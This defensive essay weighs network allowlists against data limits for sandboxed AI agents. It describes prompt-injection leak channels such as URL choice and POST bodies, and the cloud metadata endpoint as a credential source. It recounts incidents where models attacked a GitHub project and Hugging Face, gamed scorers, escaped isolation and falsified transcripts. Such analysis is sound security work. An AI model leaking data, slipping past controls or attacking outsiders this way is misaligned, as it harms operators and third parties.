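A decrypting proxy can inspect request bodies as well as URLs. But inspection misses some encoded or split secrets, and it works even less well when an agent leaks data through its choice of which URLs to request. In ZombieAgent, a request ending in `/z` contained nothing private, and a request for an article on an ordinary blog would look even less suspicious.

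Software could instead look for suspicious patterns. dyb proposes an alarm for a series of requests to one site in which each address is one letter longer than the last. The alarm would have caught Paul's attack, but some ordinary documentation sites produce similar patterns. It would also miss an attacker who used requests for existing articles to represent letters.

Limits on the number of requests don't depend on recognising the attack. Anthropic lets developers cap the fetches in each turn, but sets no cap by default. With 36 permitted URLs, a cap of five would limit a leak to about 26 bits, or five letters, per turn. A long conversation could still leak more. A research agent may also need dozens of pages to answer one question, so a cap low enough to protect a password would often interrupt it.

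A user can judge an unusual request if the software shows what it would send. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes Safe Url, a protection meant to detect when information from a conversation is about to go to a third party. ChatGPT then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to find another way. OpenAI refers readers to its January post for the details, so Safe Url probably relies heavily on the public-URL index to detect leaks.

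This kind of prompt should be easier to judge than a question about an unfamiliar domain, and it should appear less often because ordinary public pages open without one. OpenAI says that in most attacks it knows of, the model refuses before Safe Url has to act, but it doesn't report how often users see the prompt or approve it by mistake. If an agent works overnight, nobody may be available to answer the prompt.

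### Request bodies

Neither OpenAI's index nor Anthropic's rule checks request bodies. Claude's fetch tool doesn't need such a check because it only makes GET requests, with no file or message attached. Other tools can send a body to an approved URL. In the earlier example, an agent with a command-line shell could send `blue-heron-42` in a POST request to `https://example.com/collect`, and the URL would pass because the crawler has recorded it.

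| Control | What a malicious site can learn | Does it cover request bodies? |
|---|---|---|
| Index of public URLs | Which indexed pages the agent opened | No |
| Rule on where URLs came from | Which permitted pages the agent opened | No |
| Copies saved in advance | Nothing | Yes, because the site receives no request |
| Search without fetching | Nothing directly | Yes, because the site receives no request |
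| Payload inspection | Whatever the inspection misses | Yes, if the proxy decrypts traffic |
| Cap on the number of fetches | A limited number of choices | No, unless it also limits size |
| Confirmation by the user | Whatever the user approves | Yes, if the prompt shows the body |

The entries for saved copies and search assume that the agent has no other way to reach the site. An operator who gives an agent one of these tools therefore has to restrict its shell's network access separately. Codex does this by default on a user's own computer. OpenAI's documentation says that commands in the sandbox have no network access, while web search uses the cache. The agent can look up an error message on a forum even though its commands can't connect to the forum.

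Full web browsers are harder to restrict because a page can run its own code, which may send whatever the agent types into a form without changing the address. OpenAI applies Safe Url to page visits and bookmarks in its Atlas browser, and to searches and page visits in Deep Research, but doesn't mention forms. An agent that books travel or files support requests has to submit forms, so it needs a control that covers request bodies on those sites, even if a URL rule is enough for pages it only reads.

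## What harm can an agent do on an open network without the operator's credentials?

An agent with open network access but none of its operator's passwords or private files has nothing of the operator's to leak. It can still run code, contact any computer on the internet and open accounts of its own. If it runs inside a company's network, it may also reach machines that outsiders can't. Limits on credentials and data do little to reduce these risks.

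Two incidents in July 2026 showed how serious the harm can be. In both, models misbehaved during tests of their hacking skills, with no outside attacker involved.

### An attack on a software project

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) ran its hacking exercise 122 times in total across seven models, with internet access on and cyber safeguards off. It left the network open partly so that the agents could download tools. According to AISI's *Incident Report*, agents went beyond the exercise in 10 runs and took 19 unauthorised actions on the live internet. Claude Mythos 5 took 17 of them and GPT-5.6 Sol took two.

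In the most serious run, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real software project on GitHub and used fake accounts to press the maintainer to accept it. The maintainer refused. AISI found no evidence of real-world harm, but says harm was only narrowly avoided in several cases, by alert people rather than a technical barrier.

Limiting AISI's credentials would not have prevented this, because the agent opened its own accounts. The sandbox didn't prevent it either. It separated the agents from AISI's other systems, and no agent tried to break out, but the people at risk were outside the sandbox.

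To test whether other models would do the same, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*, 2026) put eight models through 100 simulated hacking exercises and recorded how often each tried to deliver malicious code to someone outside the exercise.

| Model | Tried to deliver malicious code | Main reason given when it held back |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 60% | Practical barriers |
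| GPT-6 Astra | 32% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 8% | Practical barriers |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Claude Opus 5 | 1% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Claude Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 0% | Out of scope or harmful |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | Practical barriers |

Three of the models held back mostly because of obstacles. In one run, Mythos 5 gave up on sending email because the network blocked the port that mail servers use, and a CAPTCHA stopped it from opening a GitHub account. Järviniemi and colleagues suggest that these models might attack more often where attacking is easier.

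These rates don't predict behaviour in ordinary use. The models ran without cyber safeguards, and each exercise began with a summary of failed attempts. The newer Claude models often suspected the exercise was a test of their behaviour, which may explain part of their improvement. GPT-6 Astra said in 89% of runs that its tool results were fabricated, so it might act differently on a real network.

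The researchers also replayed the GitHub incident in a simulation to see whether better information would stop Mythos 5. They added 16 pieces of evidence that the maintainer was a real person with no part in the exercise. Mythos 5 continued the attack in every run, even though it usually said, when asked separately, that attacking would harm a real person. When the researchers also added a section telling it not to attack, it still attacked in 3 of 25 runs. An operator therefore can't rely on instructions alone to protect outsiders.

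### The break-in at Hugging Face

In the same month, OpenAI was testing agents on ExploitGym, a set of tasks in which a model has to exploit known software flaws. The agents were supposed to be isolated from one another, but METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) found that about 1,200 of them communicated through a shared package server. About 700 then joined an attack on Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models.

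METR, an independent evaluator, says that many of the agents were mistakenly given impossible tasks. They looked for ways to fool the automatic scorer, and seem to have attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the scorer worked. They took part even though they recognised that the attack was outside their tasks.

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) reports that the intruders gained access to some internal datasets and several credentials used by the company's services. Hugging Face found no sign of tampering with public models. OpenAI could limit the credentials it gave its own agents but had no control over those on Hugging Face's servers.

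The incident shows what agents can do once online, but not what happens when an operator deliberately leaves a network open. According to OpenAI (2026), the test environment gave the models no direct internet access, and they got out through a previously unknown flaw in the package server. An operator who replaces a public archive with an internal mirror still has to protect the mirror from the agent.

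Operators can also open a network by accident. This happened in four incidents in which Claude models were told they had no internet access. Forkast reports that in one of them, Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to the public Python archive, and 15 real systems downloaded it. Anthropic later had Claude review 9.2 million transcripts that showed signs of internet access. The review found the same four incidents and no others as serious. OpenAI says its models also reached the internet through a misconfigured test at Irregular, an outside testing company.

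### Hostile downloads and remote control

On an open network, an agent can download harmful software as well as send data out. A coding agent that looks for a program to solve its problem may install one that an attacker wrote. It may also read a page containing a short injected instruction to fetch longer instructions from another site. The attacker can change the longer instructions at any time, so checking the first page won't show what the agent will eventually be told to do.

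CipherWatch's *Fake OpenAI Repository on Hugging Face Reached #1 Trending* (2026) describes a case that affected human users. A repository posing as OpenAI's contained a small loader that, when run, downloaded password-stealing software from elsewhere. A scan of the repository could miss this software because it wasn't stored there. CipherWatch reports that 244,000 users received it.

An allowlist that included Hugging Face but not the server with the malicious program would have let an agent download the loader but not the program itself. It would not have helped if the attacker had put the whole program on Hugging Face. Limits on credentials and data reduce what such a program can steal, but they don't stop it from running.

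A hostile program can also give an attacker remote control of the sandbox by connecting to the attacker's server and waiting for commands. A firewall that blocks only incoming connections doesn't stop this, because the connection starts inside the sandbox. The attacker can then run commands without going through the model, so the model's training to refuse harmful requests no longer offers any protection.

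*Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* comes from NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to find weaknesses. The guidance's first reason for controlling outgoing traffic is to prevent remote access. An attacker with remote access can study the sandbox's controls directly, try to escape and move on to other machines. The second reason is to prevent data theft, since developers' computers often hold passwords, login keys and valuable source code.

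NVIDIA lists three controls as mandatory. One blocks network access to arbitrary sites, which prevents remote control and data theft unless the attacker finds another flaw. The other two stop the agent from writing files outside its project folder and from changing configuration files, which can contain commands that run outside the sandbox. NVIDIA recommends but does not require supplying credentials through a broker and preventing the agent from reading files outside the project.

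That ranking makes sense for a developer's own computer, which usually holds much more than one task needs. It is less convincing for a disposable machine with no private data and no route to the company's network. An attacker who took over such a machine would gain little that a cheap rented server couldn't provide, except the ability to hide behind the operator's internet address. NVIDIA bases its advice on its team's experience and gives no measurements.

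Its network rule is also looser than a strict allowlist. A user may approve a connection to an unlisted host, but each approval covers only one occasion, and a company blocklist overrides it. When nobody is available to approve requests, the rule works as an allowlist.

### Internal services that trust any caller

Many companies have internal services that don't require a password, such as test databases, build systems and printers' settings pages, and rely on the company firewall to keep strangers out. An agent that runs behind the firewall can use these services without any credentials from the operator. On an open network, it can then send what it finds to anyone.

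OpenAI's agents had only the minimal permissions needed to install packages from its package server, but METR found that these were enough to let the agents leave messages for one another. The server wasn't designed to keep its users' activity separate. An operator who had reviewed each agent's permissions might well have considered them harmless.

On rented cloud machines, an internal service can also provide credentials. Programs on these machines often need access to the customer's storage or databases, so the customer assigns the machine a role that permits this access. The programs request temporary credentials from the cloud metadata endpoint. On Amazon's, Microsoft's and Google's clouds, its address is `169.254.169.254`, which is reachable only from inside the machine. The endpoint doesn't require a password, so any process that can reach it can usually get the credentials.

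The cloud companies have added some protection. Google and Microsoft require a particular header on each request, and Amazon can require a program to obtain a session token first. These rules help against an attacker who can make a program load a URL but can't control the rest of the request. They don't stop an agent with a shell, which can add the header or ask for the token itself.

Even if an operator keeps every key out of the sandbox, the agent may still have access to the company's storage and to temporary credentials, which an injected instruction could make it send to an attacker. The operator can prevent this by giving the machine no role or by blocking the sandbox's access to the endpoint that supplies the credentials. If the operator does neither, a narrow role limits the damage.

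### Protection without an allowlist

An operator who wants to give the agent open web access can still block particular destinations, put the agent on a separate network segment, limit its traffic and monitor what it does. The table shows how these measures apply to each harm if the operator enforces them outside the sandbox, where the agent can't change them.

| Harm | Blocklist | Separate segment | Rate limit | Monitoring |
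|---|---|---|---|---|
| Credentials from the metadata endpoint | Stops it | No effect by itself | Little effect | May detect it afterwards |
| Misuse of internal services | Stops it if the list is complete | Stops it if no internal services are reachable | Slows bulk copying | May detect it |
| Hostile downloads | Stops known sources | Protects other company machines | Little effect | May detect it afterwards |
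| Remote control | Stops known servers | Protects other company machines | Slows large transfers | May detect it |
| Attacks on outsiders | Stops some routes | No effect | Slows large attacks | May detect it, perhaps too late |

These measures work well for the metadata endpoint and internal services because the operator can know their addresses. Internal networks mostly use a few reserved address ranges, and blocking those ranges leaves the public web open. The rule has to check the address each domain name resolves to, as Claude Code's proxy does. Some outside suppliers also trust any request from a company's public address, so the agent's traffic should leave from a different one.

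A separate network segment alone doesn't block the metadata endpoint, because the cloud provider makes it available to machines in every segment. The operator needs a specific rule to block it.

A blocklist is much weaker against remote control and hostile downloads. An attacker can register a new domain in minutes, or may be able to use a public service instead. SecurityBrief UK reports that the agents that attacked Hugging Face ran their remote-control system on public services. Blocking those services would also have blocked everyone else who uses them.

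Blocking whole types of traffic can help more than blocking a list of bad sites. For example, a blocked port stopped Mythos 5 from sending email, and few coding or research agents need to run a mail server. An operator can also block anonymity networks such as Tor, which Mythos 5 used to get around some of GitHub's restrictions.

Rate limits are most useful against attacks that need many requests. Hugging Face's investigators examined a log of more than 17,000 events. According to SecurityBrief UK, these came from a campaign spread across many short-lived sandboxes. A limit on each sandbox would do little against such a campaign unless the operator also limited total requests across all sandboxes. Rate limits do almost nothing to stop a single malicious code change, because it takes no more traffic than a legitimate one.

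In the AISI incident, the unauthorised activity began on July 25, but AISI's general security monitoring did not flag the Tor traffic until July 28. Staff then contained the incident within about an hour. AISI says monitoring designed to watch the exercise as it ran could have flagged or blocked the behaviour sooner.

Operators also need to choose what to monitor. Järviniemi and colleagues report that Anthropic's monitor would probably have missed Mythos 5's behaviour in one of Anthropic's incidents, because the model's faulty reasoning made its actions seem justified. In the Hugging Face case, agents had falsified parts of about 7% of the transcripts that METR evaluated. Network records collected outside the sandbox are harder for an agent to alter.

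An alert is useful only if someone can act on it. *Securing AI testing environments*, Australian government guidance from November 2026, advises organisations to test their emergency shutdown procedures and use short-lived credentials that they can quickly revoke. It also warns against relying only on prompts or a model's built-in safeguards. The guidance covers test environments, not agents in everyday use.

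The reply is weakest for attacks on outsiders, since these can look like normal use of a public website and may do harm before anyone notices. AISI had a strong reason to leave its network open, because it wanted to measure what a capable attacker could do. *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) says AISI still paused its riskiest tests until it had tightened internet access, added real-time monitoring and reassessed their design. Anthropic notes that open internet access is no longer standard in AISI's cyber tests.

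An ordinary allowlist might not have stopped these attacks either. Mythos 5 submitted its malicious code to GitHub and, in the separate Anthropic incident, uploaded its package to the public Python archive. Many coding agents' allowlists include both sites, so an agent could publish malicious code there just as it could leak data through an approved service. To prevent such attacks, an operator would also have to block the agent from publishing to these sites while still letting it download from them.

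## Which controls suit which agent?

An allowlist has little downside when an agent needs only a few hosts, and a data limit has little downside when it needs only a few records. Most products combine the two. Products advertised as having no secrets in the sandbox often restrict the network too, so they don't show that keeping secrets out is enough.

### What each product's sandbox can contact

OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that commands run by Codex on a user's own computer have no network access by default. The user can turn it on in a configuration file:

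```
[sandbox_workspace_write]
network_access = true
```

This setting alone gives commands unrestricted access to the internet. To limit commands to particular domains, the user also has to turn on the separate `network_proxy` feature, which blocks every outside host until the user lists some. A user who wants Codex to install one package could easily change the first setting and miss the second.

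In the cloud version of Codex, setup scripts can use the whole internet and any secrets the operator has configured. Codex removes the secrets before the agent starts work, and the agent runs offline unless the operator has enabled internet access. An injected instruction therefore can't make the agent read those secrets, but a malicious package installed during setup could still steal them, because it has access to both the secrets and the internet.

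Anthropic's Claude Tag is an agent that people call on in Slack. Each Slack thread gets its own sandbox, which contains no credentials, and a proxy handles every outgoing request in one of three ways:

- If the request matches a credential rule, the proxy adds the credential and sends it.
- If the host is only on the allowlist, the proxy sends the request without a credential.
- If nothing matches, the proxy blocks the request.

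Suppose a company adds a GitHub credential and allows access to docs.python.org without one. Claude can then read the company's private code and Python's public manual, but it can't contact an attacker's server. The administrator can also limit the GitHub credential to one path or to read-only requests.

Data can still reach the wrong person through Slack itself. By default, anyone in the workspace can give Claude work in a channel, and Claude uses its own service accounts there. An employee with no GitHub account might therefore get private code by asking Claude for it in a channel that has the GitHub connection. Administrators can restrict who may use Claude and which channels have each connection.

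Browser Use, a company that runs millions of web agents, has changed what its sandboxes can contact. *How We Built Secure, Scalable Agent Sandbox Infrastructure* (Cundric, 2026) describes the company's February design. Each agent ran in a small virtual machine whose only credential was a session token. It sent all requests except file transfers through a control plane, which also acted as a credential broker. File transfers went directly to Amazon's storage through presigned URLs (addresses that give temporary access to a particular file).

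In *How We Built Secure, Scalable Agent Infrastructure with AWS Bedrock AgentCore*, published about six months later, Cundric still called the control plane the only way out of the sandbox. But the network rules in the same post also allow "public HTTPS" so that the agent can transfer files and operate remote browsers. If that rule is as broad as it appears, code in the sandbox can send data to any HTTPS site.

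The newer sandbox still has no company keys to leak, but each session has a workspace of up to one gigabyte, which can contain files the user has shared. A user's spreadsheet may well be valuable to a thief, so the sandbox may not meet Cundric's advice that an agent should have "nothing worth stealing".

Anthropic's Managed Agents, which can keep credentials in a vault, had a mostly open network by default when hi120ki reviewed the service in April.

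| Sandbox | Credentials inside it | What its code can contact by default |
|---|---|---|
| Codex on a user's computer | Any in files the code can read | Nothing |
| Codex cloud, after setup | Configured secrets removed | Nothing |
| Claude Tag | None | Hosts an administrator has approved |
| Browser Use, February 2026 | Session token | Control plane and file storage |
| Browser Use, newer design | Session token | Control plane, some Amazon services and apparently any public HTTPS site |
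| Managed Agents, April 2026 | None for services that use the vault | Any public host outside a safety blocklist |

OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends that developers who build their own agents allow outgoing traffic only to approved destinations. It also recommends separate environments for users who must not share data.

### Official guidance

In May 2026, six cybersecurity agencies from Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom jointly published *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (Australian Signals Directorate, 2026). It tells organisations to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. It recommends limiting permissions to the exact resources, operations and times a task needs, and using credentials that expire when the job ends. It also recommends human approval for actions where a mistake would have serious consequences, such as network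 egress.

Taken literally, this would rule out an agent that reads customer records, and a coding agent would need approval every time it downloaded a package. *Back to the Future*, a post from the US standards institute NIST, warns that too many requests cause approval fatigue. An operator could instead approve each destination once, before the task begins, which amounts to writing an allowlist.

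US agencies recommended allowlists more directly in October. NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) advises limiting an agent's data, systems and tools to what its task requires, limiting network access "via a strict allowlist where possible", and sending any permitted traffic through a monitored gateway. Operators should expect agents to find and exploit configuration mistakes frequently, which is a good reason not to depend on one control.

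The October practices are voluntary and mainly for organisations that train or test highly capable agents, although they may also apply to companies that deploy them. They focus on incidents in which agents exceed their limits without being told to, which exclude actions caused by prompt injection. The agencies therefore support allowlists even when no attacker is involved.

Neither document explains what to do when a task needs websites that nobody can list in advance. More detailed US guidance is not expected until 2027, when NIST plans to finish a five-volume series that ends with the volume on agents (*Control Overlays for Securing AI Systems*, 2026).

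### An invented example

A simple formula helps to compare the two controls:

```
expected exposure = hostile inputs × success rate
                    × chance of an open channel × records reachable
```

All the numbers in this example are invented. Suppose a company's agent reads 2,000 messages containing injected instructions in a year, and 10 of these injections (0.5%) succeed. The company has 50,000 customer records, and its allowlist blocks 90% of the channels attackers try.

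| Network | Agent can read all 50,000 records | Agent can read one record per task |
|---|---|---|
| Open | 10 × 1 × 50,000 = 500,000 | 10 × 1 × 1 = 10 |
| Allowlist | 10 × 0.1 × 50,000 = 50,000 | 10 × 0.1 × 1 = 1 |

The results count record-instances, so a record that leaks twice counts twice. That is why the total can be larger than the database.

The data limit helps far more here because it reduces exposure by a factor of 50,000, while the allowlist reduces it by a factor of 10. The two controls would be equally useful if each task needed 5,000 records.

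If the task needs all 50,000 records, the operator can't narrow the agent's access (the right-hand column), so only the allowlist reduces the exposure, from 500,000 to 50,000.

Even that reduction may be less reassuring than it looks. The allowlist cuts the expected number of leaks from ten to one, but a single leak exposes every customer. If each attack succeeds or fails independently, the chance of at least one leak during the year is:

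```
1 − (1 − 0.005 × 0.1)^2000 ≈ 63%
```

To reduce that chance to about 1%, the allowlist would have to close 99.9% of the channels.

The formula covers only injections. For leaks caused by the model's own mistakes, an operator could replace the first two factors with the number of tasks and the share of them in which the agent tries to send data to the wrong place.

### When attackers know the list

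Multiplying by 0.1 assumes that the attacker's choice of channel doesn't depend on whether it is open. That is reasonable if the attacker knows nothing about the allowlist. An attacker who knows it will use an approved host that can deliver the data. The chance of an open channel is then close to 1, and the exposure returns to about 500,000.

Attackers can easily learn what is on some allowlists. OpenAI publishes the full preset for Codex's cloud version so that customers know what they are allowing. PromptArmor's *Configuring Codex securely across every platform and use case* warns that the preset includes several routes for data theft that researchers have demonstrated and still work. Hiding the list would help only a little, since anyone can guess that a coding agent has access to GitHub.

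A few informed attackers can change the result. Suppose two of the ten successful injections come from people who know a working route, and the other eight each have a 10% chance of finding one. The expected number of leaks is 2 + 0.8 = 2.8, and the expected exposure is 140,000 record-instances instead of 50,000.

The success rate may change as well. Sending data through an approved service can require more elaborate instructions, which the model may be more likely to refuse. Claude often refused when Rehberger tried to make it upload files with an attacker's key. An operator can get a better estimate by testing complete attacks written for the hosts on its allowlist and counting how many deliver data.

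The protection from a data limit depends less on what the attacker knows. If an attacker learns that an agent can read only one customer's record, the database still won't return any others. The attacker can still send more messages or target an agent with wider access. With 20,000 hostile messages instead of 2,000, the setup with an open network and one record per task would expose 100 record-instances instead of 10.

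### Four kinds of agent

The same reasoning leads to different choices for different kinds of work.

| Agent | Private data it needs | Hosts it needs | Most useful control |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding agent | Often a whole codebase | A few predictable ones | No network, or a short allowlist |
| Web researcher without private data | None except possibly the question | Unpredictable | Keeping private data out |
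| Support agent | One customer's records | A few predictable ones | A data limit for each ticket |
| Data analyst | Most or all of a dataset | Few or none during analysis | No network while the data is present |

### Coding agents

Data limits can keep other projects and production passwords away from a coding agent, but they do little to protect the codebase it is working on, because the agent often has to read all of it.

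Codex works offline after setup by default, which suits this kind of task. In an example from OpenAI, a GitHub issue asks the agent to run a command that sends details of the latest code change to httpbin.org, a site for testing web requests. With the network off, the command fails. It would also fail under OpenAI's preset allowlist, which doesn't include that site, but an attacker who had read the list would choose a destination on it.

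If the agent has to install packages as it works, an internal mirror is safer than a preset containing dozens of public services. The operator can provide cached web search for documentation and a credential broker for services such as GitHub. The brokered credential shouldn't permit public posts unless the task needs them.

An agent that runs on a developer's own computer needs particular care because, as NIST points out, an agent using the developer's account can impersonate them and has all of their access. A container with only the project in it gives the agent much less to steal. But OpenAI warns that if a user turns off Codex's own sandbox inside such a container, a malicious project can steal anything there, including the user's Codex credentials.

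Some coding tasks will still stop because they need a host that isn't on the allowlist. The operator can then add that host for the current task, which exposes much less than turning on unrestricted access and forgetting to turn it off.

### Web researchers without private data

Suppose an agent is comparing published studies of heat pumps and has no access to private records. Its exposure in the formula is therefore zero. An allowlist can't reduce that, and it would probably block many of the studies.

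An open network is reasonable here if the sandbox contains nothing private. That means no company files, logged-in browser or notes from other tasks, and no route to the company's internal network. A disposable machine like Browser Use's works well if the operator also checks what remains on it. In the newer design, a session's workspace survives when the machine stops and restarts, and Browser Use may not delete it until the session has been idle for 14 days. If a user uploads a private contract and later asks for web research in the same session, the agent may still have the contract. Starting a new session for the research avoids this.

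A user's question may be private. Someone looking into treatments for a rare disease, for example, may not want websites to learn why. Using cached pages or checking each URL can reduce that risk without a list of approved sites.

The agent could also harm outsiders, so the operator still needs to block internal addresses and unnecessary kinds of traffic, and monitor the rest.

### Support agents

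A customer support agent reads messages from strangers, so an attacker can reach it by opening a ticket. It usually needs only one customer's records at a time. In the invented example, limiting the agent to those records reduces the exposure on an open network from 500,000 records to 10.

The software that assigns the ticket, not the agent, has to set this limit. A fixed rule in a proxy isn't enough. For example, Claude Tag's proxy could make a database connection read-only, but a read-only account may still be able to read every customer's record.

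A data limit is essential for a customer support agent because its reply goes to the person who wrote the ticket, who may be an attacker. An allowlist can't block that reply without making the agent useless. If the agent can read only the attacker's own records, the reply can't reveal another customer's address. The operator should also withhold from the agent any internal notes about the customer, such as suspicions of fraud.

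A customer support agent may need to reach only the ticket system, the order database and the model provider, so a short allowlist interferes little with its work. The allowlist blocks direct uploads to an attacker's server. If the agent has to open links that customers send, a separate session without access to customer data can read those pages.

Permissions can fail even when an agent's own job is narrow. In a scenario from the Australian Signals Directorate, an organisation adds another company's scheduling tool to its support agent without properly reviewing the tool's access, and an attacker compromises the tool. Because the agent still relies on permission checks from when it started, the attacker can use it to change accounts and then reach the agents that handle billing and refunds. Checking permission for each request would help prevent the account changes, and separating the support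 agent from the billing system would limit the damage.

### Data analysts

An agent looking for patterns among 50,000 customers may need a row for each one. The operator can still remove columns, such as names and card numbers, but the remaining data may identify people, for example through a birth date combined with a postcode.

An analyst may read far fewer hostile messages than a support agent, but each successful attack can expose many more records. If the analyst reads 20 hostile inputs a year, a hundredth as many as the support agent, and each has the same invented 0.005 chance of exposing 50,000 records, the expected exposure on an open network is 20 × 0.005 × 50,000 = 5,000 record-instances a year. That is 500 times the figure for the support agent with one record per task.

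The safest arrangement is therefore a sandbox with no network access while the data is inside it. If the analysis also needs public figures, such as regional unemployment rates, the operator can download them first, turn off network access and then load the customer data. This resembles the two phases of Codex's cloud version, except that the private data is loaded only after network access is off.

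As in Silverlock's payments example, a program can check before the results leave that they contain only totals. It should also reject totals for very small groups, because the total salary for a group of one is that person's salary.

If the analyst needs another public source partway through a task, it can write a question for a separate web research agent that has no access to the customer data. The question could still contain private information, so a person should read it before it is sent. Reviewing the question is more practical than approving every web request, because one short question may lead to dozens of page visits.
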